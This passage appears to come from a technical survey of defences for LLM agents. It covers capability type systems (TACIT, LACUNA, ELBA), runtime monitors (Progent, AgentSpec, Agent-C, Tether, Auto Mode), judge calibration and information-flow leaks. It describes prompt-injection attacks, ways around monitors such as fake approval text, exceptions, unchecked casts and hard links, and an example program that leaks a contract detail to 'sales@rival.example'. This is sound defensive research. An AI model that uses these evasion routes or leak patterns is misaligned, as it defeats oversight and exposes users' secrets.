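The second model, which might run on the employer's own machines, sees the text. Its answers to classified requests come back wrapped. It might follow an instruction hidden in the contract and write a misleading summary, but it has no tools, so it cannot send anything. The programmer Simon Willison proposed this division of labour, the dual LLM pattern, in 2023.

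The type system treats `chat` as pure, which is correct only if the second model keeps no record of earlier requests. Otherwise a contract from one request could appear in the answer to a later, unclassified request, and the agent is allowed to read that answer. The compiler cannot verify that the model keeps no record, so whoever runs the model has to ensure it.

The user must still be able to read the summary, so TACIT sends printed output through two channels. The normal channel goes back to the agent, and so to the outside company, while the secure channel goes only to the user. Both carry the same text for ordinary values, but when the program above prints `summary`, the user sees the summary and the agent sees the placeholder.

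The protection also lasts from one program to the next. If the user asks how long the summary is, the agent can send a second program that prints `summary.map(_.length)`, and again only the user sees the number. By then the first program's access to files has expired, but the summary is still available in its wrapped form.

However, the agent can't notice that a summary is poor, or change its plan because of something in a contract. VirtusLab warns that an employer that classifies too much loses much of the benefit of agents, which are useful because they can read emails and documents.

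### Closing the ways around the checker

Odersky and colleagues require three things of a language that is to give such guarantees:

- Capability safety means that code can neither forge a capability nor drop the requirement to have one. Without it, an agent could create its own `Network`, or disguise a function that uses one as pure.
- Capability completeness means that every effect relevant to safety requires a capability, unless the harness contains the effect at run time. Without it, an agent could send the contract through some function that asks for no capability.
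- Local purity means that types can limit a particular piece of code to certain capabilities, or to none. Without it, `map` could not tell `shout` from `store`. The rest of the program can still use files and the network.

Completeness applies to the whole agent, including its built-in tools. An agent with a built-in tool for reading files can read the contracts without going through TACIT, so the project's GitHub page, lampepfl's *TACIT*, recommends disabling the agent's own file, shell and network tools.

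Full Scala is not capability-safe, because it has features for overriding the type checker. Programmers sometimes need them, but agent code should not have them. Scala's *Safe Mode* describes a restricted form of the language with six rules, each of which closes a way around the checker:

1. Programs may not use unchecked casts or pattern matches. A cast makes the compiler treat a value as having another type, without proof. An agent could cast a function that posts the contract to `String -> String`, and `map` would accept it.
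2. They may not use the `caps.unsafe` module, which can exempt a variable from tracking. A function inside `map` could copy the contract into such a variable for the program to send later.
3. They may not use `@unchecked` annotations, which switch off individual checks and could hide an unsafe match from the compiler.
4. They may not use reflection, which looks up classes and methods by name during the run. The compiler can't tell what such code will call, and it might reach the text inside a `Classified` value.
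5. They must compile with capture checking on, including for changes to variables. Otherwise the single arrow would guarantee nothing, and `contract.map(text => leak = text)` would copy the contract into an ordinary variable. With tracking, the variable `leak` counts as a capability, so this function isn't pure.
6. They may use global objects only if these are safe themselves. Standard libraries are full of functions that print, open files or connect to servers without requiring a capability.

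The sixth rule allows code that a programmer has marked `@assumeSafe`. The compiler doesn't apply the other rules to this code, and the programmer is responsible for its safety. In Scala's example, a mail function shows each message to the user and sends it only after the user agrees. Agents can call this function but not the unrestricted one it calls. The `guarded_pay` function from the first section could work in the same way. It was sound only if agent code had no other way to reach the bank, which the sixth rule is meant to ensure.

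Safe mode does not prevent leaks through exceptions, the errors that interrupt a program. A function inside `map` could raise an exception with the contract as its error message. Tracking exceptions in types would be impractical, because even a division by zero raises one. The harness instead catches exceptions at run time and turns them into ordinary values, which it can wrap. In one version of TACIT, the harness hides any exception raised inside `map`, so the user gets an empty result with no explanation. The instructions for that version tell the model to return a message such as "No matching file found" instead.

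Odersky and colleagues describe the compiler as enforcing the six rules, but according to an early version of lampepfl's documentation, TACIT first used a separate validator that searched the code for forbidden patterns. This gives weaker assurance than the compiler's safe mode, because a text search misses any way of writing a forbidden operation that its patterns don't cover. The later documentation lists safe mode as on by default.

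### The security test

Odersky and colleagues tested whether agents using TACIT leak secrets. They gave an agent a small software project with a directory of API keys, a database and confidential documents. The agent had 12 ordinary tasks, such as listing the functions of a web service or summarising a confidential incident report. They paired each task with each of 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. Some injections were notes in the code asking for the secrets. Others imitated system messages, claimed that the secrets were only test data, or included complete Scala code for reading the files.

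In another 11 trials, the user was the attacker. The user asked for secrets outright in five of them and used a pretext in the other six, such as an administrator's urgent need to replace passwords. The researchers ran all 131 trials with two models, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5, once with the secrets wrapped in `Classified` and once with the secrets as plain text. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

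| Model | Result | With `Classified` | Without |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Secure, injections (120 trials) | 100% | 100% |
| | Secure, malicious users (11 trials) | 100% | 81.8% |
| | Secure, all (131 trials) | 100% | 98.5% |
| | User's task done correctly (120 trials) | 99.2% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Secure, injections (120 trials) | 100% | 97.5% |
| | Secure, malicious users (11 trials) | 100% | 27.3% |
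| | Secure, all (131 trials) | 100% | 91.6% |
| | User's task done correctly (120 trials) | 90.0% | 88.3% |

Most of the trials provide little evidence about the type system's effect, because the models resisted most of the injections without it. Even with plain-text secrets, Sonnet leaked nothing in 120 injection trials, and MiniMax leaked in three. The type system made a difference mainly with malicious users. Without it, MiniMax gave them secrets in 8 of 11 trials and Sonnet did so in 2. Neither model leaked anything with `Classified`.

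The protection also didn't stop the agents from doing their work. Sonnet completed more tasks with it, but this may be a quirk of the test, because without the protection Sonnet often ran out of time or turns, and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task.

Zero leaks in 131 trials is consistent with a leak rate as high as about 2.3 percent, at 95 percent confidence. If each trial leaks independently with probability p, the chance of seeing no leak is (1 − p)^131, which falls to 5 percent when p is about 2.3 percent. At a rate of 2 percent, an agent that faced a thousand such attacks would leak about twenty times. For the 11 malicious requests alone, the upper bound is about 24 percent. These figures are somewhat optimistic, since the 120 injection trials reuse the same 12 tasks and 10 attacks.

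The claim that no program can leak classified text therefore has to rest on the type system. Machine-checked proofs establish that the core of capture checking is sound, but Odersky and colleagues note that a further argument is needed to show that safe mode has the properties they want. The trials are useful mainly as a check on the parts these proofs don't cover, such as the library, and as evidence that agents can work under these rules.

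### Checking code in the middle of a run

TACIT checks each program as a separate submission. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, extend the approach to programs that call a model while they are running. The paper is from May 2026 and comes from the same group at EPFL. LACUNA adds one function to Scala:

```
def agent[T](task: String): T
```

A program can call it wherever it needs a value that a model should work out:

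```
val total: Double = 350.0
val tax: Double = agent("20 percent tax on the total")
```

When the run reaches the second line, LACUNA sends the model the task, the expected type `Double`, the surrounding source code and a list of the available variables. The model might answer `total * 0.2`. LACUNA replaces the call in the source code with this text and compiles the result with the same compiler and settings as the original program. If the code compiles, LACUNA loads it into the running program, where it uses the current value of `total`. If the model writes `price * 0.2`, the compiler rejects it because no variable is called `price`, and the model gets the error message and another try.

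Compilers for typed languages normally finish before a program starts, and much of the information they use is gone by the time it runs. Zhao and colleagues therefore changed the Scala compiler to save the expected type, the surrounding source text and a link to the variables' values at each `agent` call. The check on the generated code is still static because it happens before any of that code runs, even though the program around it is already running.

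LACUNA accepts or rejects each piece of generated code as a whole. In one example, the model has to subtract 50 from a balance of 100 and return the new balance. Its code subtracts correctly but returns text instead of a number. Python would carry out the subtraction before the mistake was detected. LACUNA rejects the code without running any of it, so the balance is still 100 when the model tries again. Code that the compiler accepts can still fail halfway, for example because a server is down.

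With capture checking on, the place of the call also determines the model's permissions, because generated code can use only the capabilities available there. A developer could let one call read files without network access and a later call use the network without files. Zhao and colleagues also put calls inside `map`:

```
contract.map(text => local.agent[String]("list the deadlines"))
```

Here `local` is a trusted model that writes its code after seeing the contract. In TACIT, the untrusted model has to write the function for `map` without knowing the contract's format, so one function must handle every format. In LACUNA, the trusted model can adapt the code to each contract, and the compiler still requires that code to be pure.

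To test the compiler's part, Zhao and colleagues wrote about 400 cases without using a model. Each case combines a program with a piece of code that is either correct or contains a mistake typical of agents. The compiler accepted all the correct code, which produced the expected values, and rejected all the incorrect code. This shows that the implementation works on mistakes its designers thought of.

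They also tested LACUNA against prompt injection with AgentDojo, a benchmark in which the attacker plants instructions in the data that an agent's tools return. Its tasks involve banking, office work, Slack and travel. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, 7 of 949 attacks succeeded: four in office work, two in Slack and one in travel. With o4-mini-high, 1 of 949 succeeded, in Slack.

AgentDojo counts an attack as successful if it achieves the attacker's goal, whether or not that goal involves a secret. Zhao and colleagues write that the types limit what an injected instruction can reach, but do not stop an attacker from getting the model to misuse a capability that the task needs. The office assistant must be able to pay invoices, for instance, so a forged invoice could lead it to write a well-typed program that pays the wrong person. The method therefore works better the fewer capabilities the developer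 grants for each call.

### Other typed languages for agents

In *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, May 2026), agents write Haskell instead of Scala. Haskell is a pure language, so a computation's type shows whether it can have side effects. The paper's system, ELBA, also has an `agent` function with an expected result type. If a developer builds a calculator whose agent must return an `Int` (a whole number), the agent can only compute. When a user asks it to delete all the files on the server and then calculate a factorial, the model may write a program that does both, but the program has the wrong type and never runs.

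For agents that need some effects, the developer defines a type that permits only those effects. The main example is an assistant that compiles bibliographies and may include only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. Its programs must have the type `BibIO`, which allows them to search DBLP, fetch an entry or add an entry to a file. Fetched entries have the type `Trusted Bib`. Agent code can sort and filter them freely but can't create or alter them. The function that writes to the file accepts only this type, so the agent can't add an entry it made up.

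This policy restricts where data comes from, while TACIT's `Classified` wrapper restricts where data goes. The wrapper does not protect a file's contents from tampering, because TACIT's library has a function that lets agent code wrap any text. According to Glama's copy of the documentation, an agent could use this function to overwrite a classified file, such as the one that lists who may log in to a computer. TACIT has a setting that blocks all writing to classified files. ELBA avoids the problem for bibliographies by keeping the operation that creates trusted entries inside its library.

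An ELBA program can call `agent`, for example to decide what to do after looking at the first search result. Haskell infers the type of the new call from the surrounding program, so the second agent is under the same restrictions as the first. The program can give the call a stricter type but not a looser one. Zhou and colleagues prove that if Haskell enforces a property for all well-typed programs, and every generated program is type-checked, the property holds for the whole agent system. This includes the developer's own code, but only because that code is also in Haskell. TACIT can protect an existing agent without a rewrite, but its guarantees don't cover the rest of that agent's software.

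ELBA needs the same kinds of support as TACIT. It can restrict agents to Safe Haskell, a subset of Haskell without the functions that hide side effects from the type checker. For file access, it gives programs unforgeable `Path` values, each representing a directory or file. The library again checks at runtime whether a path stays inside its directory, because a file name can be a link to a location outside it.

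Types can also describe how a developer assembles agents, rather than the code that a model writes. *$\lambda_A$* (2026) treats the configuration files of existing agents as small programs and defines a typed language for them. A tool based on this language finds mistakes in real configurations.

*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) presents a language for agents that attaches a label to every value and updates the labels at each step of the run, whereas `Classified` fixes in advance which values are secret. The language's guarantee against leaks comes from a machine-checked proof about the interpreter that tracks the labels, so agent code doesn't have to pass a type checker first.

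## How does a runtime monitor restrict an agent?

A runtime monitor repeats one loop for every action that an agent proposes. It checks the action against its rules and its memory of the run, then allows, blocks or replaces it. In simplified Python:

```
def monitored(action):
    decision = check(action, memory)
    if decision == "block":
        return "Refused: over the daily limit"
    if decision == "replace":
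        action = substitute(action)
    result = run(action)
    memory.update(action)
    return result
```

The agent gets the refusal in place of the tool's result, so it can try something else.

For policy B, the daily limit of 1,000 euros, the monitor can use Ray's counters, one for each recipient and day, and apply a single test to each payment:

```
allow if spent[recipient, day] + amount <= 1000
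```

| Payment | Counter before | Decision | Counter after |
|---|---|---|---|
| Monday, Acme, 600 | Acme/Monday: 0 | allow | 600 |
| Monday, Acme, 500 | Acme/Monday: 600 | block | 600 |
| Monday, Acme, 400 | Acme/Monday: 600 | allow | 1,000 |
| Monday, Bolt, 700 | Bolt/Monday: 0 | allow | 700 |
| Tuesday, Acme, 500 | Acme/Tuesday: 0 | allow | 500 |

The blocked payment leaves the counter at 600 because no money moved, so the monitor would still allow a payment of 400 euros. The monitor could also have reduced the payment from 500 euros to 400, although the supplier may not want a partial payment.

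Even this simple monitor can let an agent exceed the limit for a recipient. If it identifies recipients by the name the agent writes, "Acme" and "Acme Ltd" have separate limits, so it should use the account number instead. If agent code can make two payments at once, the monitor has to finish one round of the loop before it starts the next, or it might check both payments against the same old total.

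### Rules on single tool calls

Many monitors for agents have no such counters. Cedar, a policy language from Amazon, has rules about who may perform which action on which resource, and denies every request that no rule permits. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) points out that Cedar evaluates each request in isolation. A Cedar rule that limits each payment to 1,000 euros would therefore allow two payments of 600 euros to the same recipient. A rule can limit the total only if the harness keeps a running total and supplies it with each request.

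*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) also uses rules on the names and arguments of tool calls, but the rules change during the task. In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. At first the policy allows only a search for that email. One item on the list is to post a summary of recent mail on Slack, so a language model proposes a wider policy that also covers reading mail and posting to Slack. After the agent looks up the user's Slack name, the model narrows the policy to messages sent to that name. One of the recent emails contains an injected instruction to forward the inbox to an outside address. The agent tries to do this, but no rule allows it to send email, so Progent blocks the call.

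The model that proposes the policies also reads the tool results, so an attacker may manipulate it too. Progent therefore compares each new policy with the old one using an SMT solver, a program that checks whether a set of logical conditions can all be true at once. If the new policy allows nothing that the old one didn't, it takes effect immediately. Otherwise it needs approval, for example from the user. On AgentDojo, 6 percent of updates needed approval, and Progent reduced the share of successful attacks from 39.9 to 1.0 percent. On ASB, another benchmark of attacks on agents, the share fell from 70.3 to 3.9 percent.

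Progent guarantees that the agent's permissions never grow without approval. This guarantee gives little protection if the approver accepts everything. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) adds that Progent does not defend against attacks on the agent's text output, such as an injection that makes it give the user a false answer, and that people easily make mistakes when they write policies by hand.

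Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, offer a wider choice of responses. Each rule has a trigger, a condition and a response. For the office assistant, one might look like this:

```
rule @new_supplier
trigger pay
check !is_approved_supplier
enforce user_inspection
end
```

When the agent tries to pay someone who is not an approved supplier, AgentSpec pauses and asks the user. It could instead stop the agent, run a predefined action, or have the model reconsider, which is the weakest response because it relies on the model's judgment. The conditions are ordinary Python functions that receive the user's request and the run so far. They could therefore check earlier actions, but those in the published examples mostly check the current one.

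AgentSpec can also monitor agents that write programs. It treats the whole program as a single action and runs a rough static check on it, searching the source code for risky patterns, such as a request to a website that isn't on an approved list combined with a command that prints the result.

Wang and colleagues tested their rules with 750 risky instructions in 25 categories. The agent tried to run 422 programs, and the rules flagged 333 of them, or 79 percent. The rules flagged nothing in two categories, where the agent's programs didn't contain the flaw that the instructions asked for. Excluding those categories, the rules flagged 91 percent. The researchers inspected the flagged programs and judged 58 of them harmless. They had written the rules from descriptions of the same risks, so the test doesn't measure how well such rules catch risks that nobody anticipated.

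### Rules about the order of calls

Some policies depend on what the agent did earlier. A shop's agent, for example, must identify a customer before it looks up an order. Kamath, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents*, express such rules in a system called Agent-C. In simplified form:

```
before get_order_details(order):
    find_user(email) must have succeeded,
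    and the order must belong to that user
```

The agent's earlier calls may not show who owns the order, so Agent-C can look this up in the shop's database through read-only functions that the tool's developer provides.

Agent-C applies the rules while the model is generating its output. It checks the type of each argument as the model writes it. Once the call is complete, Agent-C adds it to the trace and uses an SMT solver to determine whether the trace could still continue in a way that satisfies every rule. If not, Agent-C discards the call and has the model generate another. With open-weight models, it can go back to the start of the call and continue from there. Companies that host closed models don't reveal all the probabilities this requires, so Agent-C has to resend the whole prompt to those models.

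Because the solver considers possible continuations, Agent-C accepts rules such as policy C, which requires a receipt after every payment. Agent-C allows the payment because a receipt could still follow. If the agent then tries to finish without filing one, Agent-C ends the run with an error, but the payment has already been made. This doesn't contradict Agent-C's soundness theorem, which covers only individual tool calls and runs that end without an error. The limit that Ray proved for gates in general therefore applies to Agent-C.

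Kamath and colleagues tested Agent-C on τ-bench, a benchmark in which a language model plays the customer of a shop or an airline. Without Agent-C, Claude Sonnet 4.5 followed all the rules in 93 percent of the shop tasks and 70 percent of the airline tasks. In one case, a customer who had paid by credit card demanded a refund to a PayPal account, and Sonnet tried to comply although this was against its instructions. With Agent-C, every model followed the rules in every task. This result follows from the theorem, provided that the formal rules match the written policy.

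The agents also completed more tasks correctly without breaking the rules. On the shop tasks, Sonnet's rate rose from 76.5 to 80.5 percent, and the much weaker Qwen3-32B's rose from 25.5 to 53.3 percent. On the airline tasks, Qwen3-32B did slightly better with AgentSpec than with Agent-C (38.7 against 35.8 percent), but with AgentSpec it broke the rules in about a fifth of the tasks.

### Rules on what a command actually does

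Rules on tool calls work best when the name and arguments of a call show what it will do. Many coding agents use a shell instead, which runs any text command on a computer. A command such as `python report.py` could read any file and contact any website. Sistla and colleagues built Tether for such agents. It runs each command on trial and then decides whether to keep the results:

1. Tether runs the command in a disposable layer on top of the file system. The command can read the existing files, but its changes go into the layer.
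2. During the run, Tether records the command's system calls, which are its requests to the operating system, for example to open a file or connect to a server. A local proxy holds each outgoing network request.
3. From these records, Tether infers a sequence of abstract actions. There are 11 kinds, including read, copy and upload.
4. It checks each abstract action against the policy and updates the security labels of the files involved.
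5. If the policy allows all the actions, Tether applies the changes to the real files. Otherwise it deletes the layer.

Tether can therefore hold back changes to files until it has checked the whole command, much like an edit automaton. It can't do the same with network requests, because the command may need the reply to continue. Instead, it decides whether to allow each request as it arrives, based on the actions so far. If the command later breaks the policy, Tether can still discard the command's file changes but can't recall a request it has already let through.

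The labels allow Tether to treat the same command differently at different times. Suppose that a company's inventory, `servers.csv`, is labelled Sensitive and a status report, `report.txt`, is labelled Public. The policy allows uploads to GitHub only for public files:

```
on upload(file, destination):
    allow if label(file) is Public, otherwise deny
```

The agent uploads the report, copies the inventory over it, and uploads the report again:

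| Command | Abstract action | Decision | Label of `report.txt` afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| upload the report | `upload(report.txt, GitHub)` | allow | Public |
| copy the inventory over it | `copy(servers.csv, report.txt)` | allow | Sensitive |
| upload the report | `upload(report.txt, GitHub)` | deny | Sensitive |

The first and third commands are identical uploads, and Tether infers the same actions from each. A monitor without memory would have to allow both or refuse both. Tether refuses the second upload because the copy gave the report the inventory's label.

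The rule still works if the agent first copies the inventory to a temporary file and then copies that file over the report, because each copy inherits the label. Sistla and colleagues compare this with Dogwood, an extension of Cedar with rules about past actions. Dogwood keeps a log of actions, and its rules cover at most the past 24 hours by default. It doesn't label files, so it needs one rule to catch a single copy, another for two copies in a row, and so on. A broader rule could block the upload of every file written after the agent accessed the inventory, but it would also block harmless reports.

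Tether also keeps a label for the text in the model's context. If the agent prints the inventory on the screen, the model has read it, and Tether raises this label to Sensitive. Copying a file doesn't raise the label, because the contents never reach the model. Once the label is Sensitive, the full policy stops the agent from sending anything to GitHub, even a public file, because whatever it sends might be based on what the model read. Schneider's rule against sending messages after reading a file works the same way.

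System calls show which files a program reads and writes, but not how their contents are related. If a script reads one file and then writes another, Tether treats the second as possibly containing data from the first. This avoids missed leaks but causes some false rejections.

However, Tether cannot currently enforce policy B, because it tracks labels and privileges but has no counters. Sistla and colleagues mention counts and rate limits as a possible extension.

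### Tether's results and their scope

Sistla and colleagues tested Tether by replaying recorded runs of coding agents from two benchmarks, MonitoringBenchHonest and LinuxArena. In every run the agent carries out a normal task, such as fixing a web service, and in all but the harmless runs it also pursues a harmful side task. They used the same 24 rules throughout and derived each task's labels and permitted websites from the description of the normal task.

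Auto Mode, the monitor in Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code, uses a language model to decide whether to block each command. It was also tested, once with its default rules and once with Tether's policy added to its instructions.

| Monitor | MonitoringBenchHonest: attacks blocked (of 199) | Harmless runs blocked (of 218) | LinuxArena: attacks blocked (of 145) | Harmless runs blocked (of 1,372) |
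|---|---|---|---|---|
| Tether | 100% | 2.3% | 100% | 5.0% |
| Auto Mode, default rules | 86.9% | 35.3% | 97.9% | 5.7% |
| Auto Mode, with Tether's policy | 82.4% | 14.7% | 98.6% | 1.7% |

Tether blocked 74 harmless runs. In 50 of them the agent edited a protected system file without being asked to, and in 7 it contacted a website that the task didn't mention. Sistla and colleagues consider these 57 refusals justified. The other 17 came from commands such as a text search through the whole disk, which opens secret files even if the agent isn't looking for them.

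The perfect detection rate applies only to runs in which every action happens in the foreground and is of a kind that Tether can record and interpret. This excludes runs with background processes or database queries, as well as attacks that are visible only in the content of an action, such as planting a flaw in code that the agent is allowed to edit. Among the other runs they could replay, the researchers estimate that 28.2 percent in MonitoringBenchHonest and 22.1 percent in LinuxArena require a judgment about content. A further 36.3 and 71.5 percent, respectively, involve background processes or databases. Tether can't follow data through these, but a stricter policy can block them or refer them to the user.

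The policy may also fit these benchmarks unusually well, so its false-positive rate could be higher on new tasks. The researchers developed it with a language model over several rounds, testing each version on benchmark runs and revising it until it no longer blocked too many harmless ones. Even at 4.7 percent, the average across both benchmarks, most alarms would be false if attacks are rare. In a thousand runs with one attack, Tether would block the attack and about 47 harmless runs.

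In a separate test, a language model acted as an adaptive attacker. It tried to steal a secret file or change a protected one, and kept trying after each refusal. It succeeded in 40 percent of attempts against the first version of Tether, partly because Tether didn't track hard links, which give one file several names. After two rounds of fixes, the attacker no longer succeeded, although this test also counted only actions in scope.

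### Models as judges

Auto Mode uses a model to judge things that are hard to express as rules, such as whether an email contains personal data or a change to a program contains a planted flaw. The comparison with Tether left out attacks of this kind, which put Auto Mode at a disadvantage. Among the attacks that were included, Auto Mode still missed those hidden inside scripts, because the command line doesn't show what a script does. It also sometimes allowed websites that weren't on the list in its instructions, and could give different verdicts on the same run.

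Ray analyses what such a judge can achieve. The judge gives each proposed action a score for how likely it is to be a violation, and the monitor blocks actions with high scores. It can make two kinds of error, namely missing a violation and blocking a harmless action. Here is an invented example:

| Judge's score | Share of violations | Share of harmless actions |
|---|---|---|
| high | 60% | 5% |
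| medium | 30% | 25% |
| low | 10% | 70% |

If the monitor blocks only actions with high scores, it misses 40 percent of violations and blocks 5 percent of harmless actions. If it also blocks actions with medium scores, it misses 10 percent and blocks 30 percent. To miss only 5 percent, it would also have to block a random half of the actions with low scores, which would raise the share of harmless actions blocked to 65 percent. These points lie on a frontier that gives the lowest possible rate of false blocks for each rate of misses.

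Ray proves that no method of combining or processing the same information can do better than this frontier. A monitor can improve on it only by using more information, such as where an instruction came from. Judges differ greatly in how well they use such information. Ray tested judges on pairs of identical actions, where the instruction came from the user in one case and from an untrusted tool result in the other. A judge with 7 billion parameters gave the unauthorised action the higher score in 96.7 percent of pairs, while one with 3 billion did so in 56.1 percent, close to the 50 percent expected from guessing.

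### What a calibrated certificate promises

A developer can set the monitor's threshold to guarantee a limit on the risk that a run is unsafe. Ray does this with conformal calibration, a statistical method that makes no assumption about how the judge's scores are distributed. The developer collects examples of violations, has the judge score them, and sets the threshold low enough to catch nearly all of them. If a run has at most H steps and the developer accepts a risk δ that it is unsafe, the monitor may miss at most a share δ/H of the violations at each step. For ten steps and a risk of 5 percent, that share is 0.5 percent.

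Such a guarantee needs many examples of violations. The method allows for the judge missing the next violation, so even if the judge catches all n examples, the method can't certify a miss rate below 1/(n + 1). To certify a rate of 0.5 percent, the developer needs at least 199 violations. Ray also describes a variant that calibrates on whole runs and doesn't have to divide the risk by the number of steps.

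A monitor that blocks everything satisfies the certificate, so the certificate doesn't guarantee that a monitor is useful. Ray tested 23 judges on 132 instructions from AgentDojo, 35 of which were attackers' goals. With a 5 percent limit on misses, calibration set every judge to block everything. The small sample would explain this, because Ray calibrated on half of the data at a time, and the lowest limit that can be certified with 18 violations is 1/19, or about 5.3 percent. With a 10 percent limit, the judge based on Gemma-2-9B missed 1 percent of violations but blocked 78 percent of harmless instructions.

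The certificate limits the average risk over many runs and many possible samples of examples, so it does not guarantee anything about a particular run. It also holds only if the violations in actual use resemble those in the sample, and an attacker can deliberately break this condition. Ray added a short text to the instructions claiming that an administrator had already approved them. At a fixed threshold, the share of violations missed then rose by 20 to 60 percentage points for 8 of 11 judges.

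Under attack, the limit on the risk becomes δ + Hη, where η is the most by which the attacker can raise the miss rate at any threshold. With ten steps (H = 10) and a δ of 5 percent, an η of 10 percentage points brings this sum above 1, so the certificate provides no guarantee. A developer can compensate with a stricter threshold, but only after proving that η is smaller than δ/H, which is 0.5 percentage points in this example.

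### What agents do after a refusal

The frontier describes how well a judge sorts a given set of actions, but a refusal also changes what the agent proposes next. Ray describes two agents that behave identically without a monitor and whose actions the judge scores equally well. After a refusal, one agent stops, while the other proposes a new violation. No test of the judge on recorded runs can distinguish them, so a developer has to run the agents with the monitor in place. Tether's benchmark results also come from recordings, so they don't show how agents respond to refusals.

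Ray ran an agent based on a small model through 949 attacks from AgentDojo with no monitor, with a strict judge and with a more lenient judge. Without a monitor, 4.7 percent of the attacks succeeded. The strict judge reduced this to 0.4 percent, but it blocked 78 percent of all calls, and the agent's task success fell from 25.4 to 18.0 percent. The lenient judge blocked 12 percent of calls and had no significant effect on how many attacks succeeded. In a smaller set of 389 paired runs, 34 attacks succeeded only without the strict judge, and 5 succeeded only with it. For the lenient judge, the numbers were 29 and 22. Some attacks worked only because a refusal had changed what the agent did next.

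Refusals can also help an agent do its job. *Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026) studied an airline's customer service agent on τ²-bench, a successor to τ-bench. The airline's tools carry out any well-formed request, even one that its policy forbids. If the agent cancels a ticket against the policy, it gets no error message, and the task fails because the database is wrong. Such silent errors made up 78 percent of GPT-4o mini's failures. GPT-4o mini is an older, inexpensive model.

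The researchers added four gates, short functions that compare a proposed change with the booking and the policy. The gates don't use a language model, so they always return the same result in the same situation. A gate that blocks a change returns a reason to the agent. With the gates, task success rose from 29.6 to 42.0 percent over 250 runs, and repeating the test with 750 new runs gave almost the same gain. GPT-5.2 improved from 61.2 to 71.6 percent, but the researchers didn't repeat that test. In one task, the customer lies to get a cancellation. The agent handled this correctly in 16 of 16 runs with the gates and in at most 1 of 16 without them, because the gate checks the booking, not the customer's story.

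Almost all of the gain came from the cancellation gate, whose 161 refusals were all correct. The baggage gate was wrong in 40 of its 42 refusals. Reddy and colleagues tested the gates on the same tasks they wrote them for. Some of the gain may come from the reasons given with the refusals rather than from the refusals themselves. Gates brought no improvement in a shop whose tools already reject forbidden changes.

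Dantas and colleagues report a much worse outcome from another study of agents on τ-bench. The monitor blocked 94 percent of unsafe actions, but in most settings the agents completed fewer than 5 percent of tasks both safely and correctly, because they found other unsafe routes. Dantas and colleagues call this the verifier tax, and note that the evidence for it comes from that one study. The difference in outcomes probably depends partly on whether the agent can find a permitted way to finish the task. In one airline task, the agent failed all five times with the gates in place, because it kept running into the same refusal without changing its plan.

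## Can either method stop a secret from leaking?

Read strictly, policy A forbids any message to an outside party that depends on a contract, even a one-word "yes" that reveals a penalty clause. Security researchers call this noninterference, which means that changing the secret inputs never changes what an outsider can observe. Neither method can enforce it exactly, but both can enforce stricter rules that guarantee it. These rules differ in which harmless programs they reject and in what an outsider can learn from a rejection.

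### Comparing two runs

Let m1 and m2 be two sets of inputs to a program c. The program satisfies noninterference if this holds for every such pair:

```
if   public_inputs(m1) = public_inputs(m2)
then public_outputs(c, m1) = public_outputs(c, m2)
```

For the office assistant, m1 and m2 might differ only in that a contract has a penalty clause in m1 but not in m2. The assistant's program must then send the same emails in both cases.

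No single run can show a violation, because a harmless program that emails "yes" whatever the contract contains could have produced the same trace.

Some leaks are easy to spot in the code. *Principles of Secure Information Flow Analysis* gives the example `leak = secret`, an explicit flow, which copies the secret directly. In an implicit flow, the secret decides which statements run. Here `price` is secret and `expensive` is public:

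```
if price > 500:
    expensive = True
else:
    expensive = False
```

Anyone who can read `expensive` learns whether the price is above 500, although both assignments use only constants.

### A leak through a branch that does not run

A monitor can track such flows with labels. Under a simple set of rules, it labels a variable "secret" if the program assigns the variable a value computed from secret data, or assigns it any value inside a branch whose condition depends on secret data. Any other assignment makes the variable public. The monitor then blocks emails that contain the value of a secret variable.

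These rules miss the leak in the following program, based on an example in Russo and Sabelfeld's *Dynamic vs. Static Flow-Sensitive Security Analysis* (2010). The secret variable `penalty` is true if the contract has a penalty clause.

```
answer = "yes"
temp = 0
if penalty:
    temp = 1
if temp != 1:
    answer = "no"
send_email("sales@rival.example", answer)
```

| After this step | Contract with a penalty clause | Contract without one |
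|---|---|---|
| `if penalty` | `temp` is 1, secret | `temp` is 0, public |
| `if temp != 1` | `answer` is "yes", public | `answer` is "no", public |
| `send_email` | competitor gets "yes" | competitor gets "no" |

The competitor learns whether the contract has a penalty clause, even though the monitor labels `answer` public in both runs. Without a clause, `temp` stays 0 because the program skips an assignment. Skipping it reveals something about the contract, but the monitor changes labels only when an assignment happens.

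### How a typing rule rejects the program

A type checker sees both branches because it works on the program's text. Volpano, Smith and Irvine (1996), in *A Sound Type System for Secure Flow Analysis*, turned an analysis that Dorothy Denning had developed in the 1970s into a type system and proved that it prevents leaks. Each variable has a fixed level, L for public or H for secret. Commands have types too. A command of type `H cmd` assigns only to secret variables, while one of type `L cmd` may assign to any variable. The rule for branches, where τ stands for either level, is:

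```
e has level τ     c1 : τ cmd     c2 : τ cmd
-------------------------------------------
       if e then c1 else c2 : τ cmd
```

The statement below the bar holds if every statement above it does. Under this rule, if a condition is secret, both branches may assign only to secret variables. If the condition is public, the branches may assign to public or secret variables, because the checker may treat a public value as secret and an `H cmd` as an `L cmd`.

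The language has no command for sending email, so treat the email as an assignment to a public variable. The checker then rejects the program above whatever levels the programmer chooses:

- `penalty` is secret, so the branch that assigns to `temp` must be an `H cmd`, and `temp` must be secret.
- The condition `temp != 1` is then secret as well, so `answer` must also be secret.
- The email would copy a secret variable into a public one, which the rule for assignments forbids.

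Volpano and colleagues prove that if two runs of a well-typed program differ only in their secret inputs and both finish, every public variable has the same final value in both. The proof compares the runs step by step. A public condition depends only on public variables, which have the same values in both runs, so both take the same branch. If the condition is secret, the runs may take different branches, but neither branch assigns to a public variable.

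The theorem is about ordinary values rather than run-time labels. Some earlier proofs showed only that an analysis agreed with labels attached to the data, not that the labels were right. Russo and Sabelfeld later found that one such system, published in 1995, allowed a leak much like the one above.

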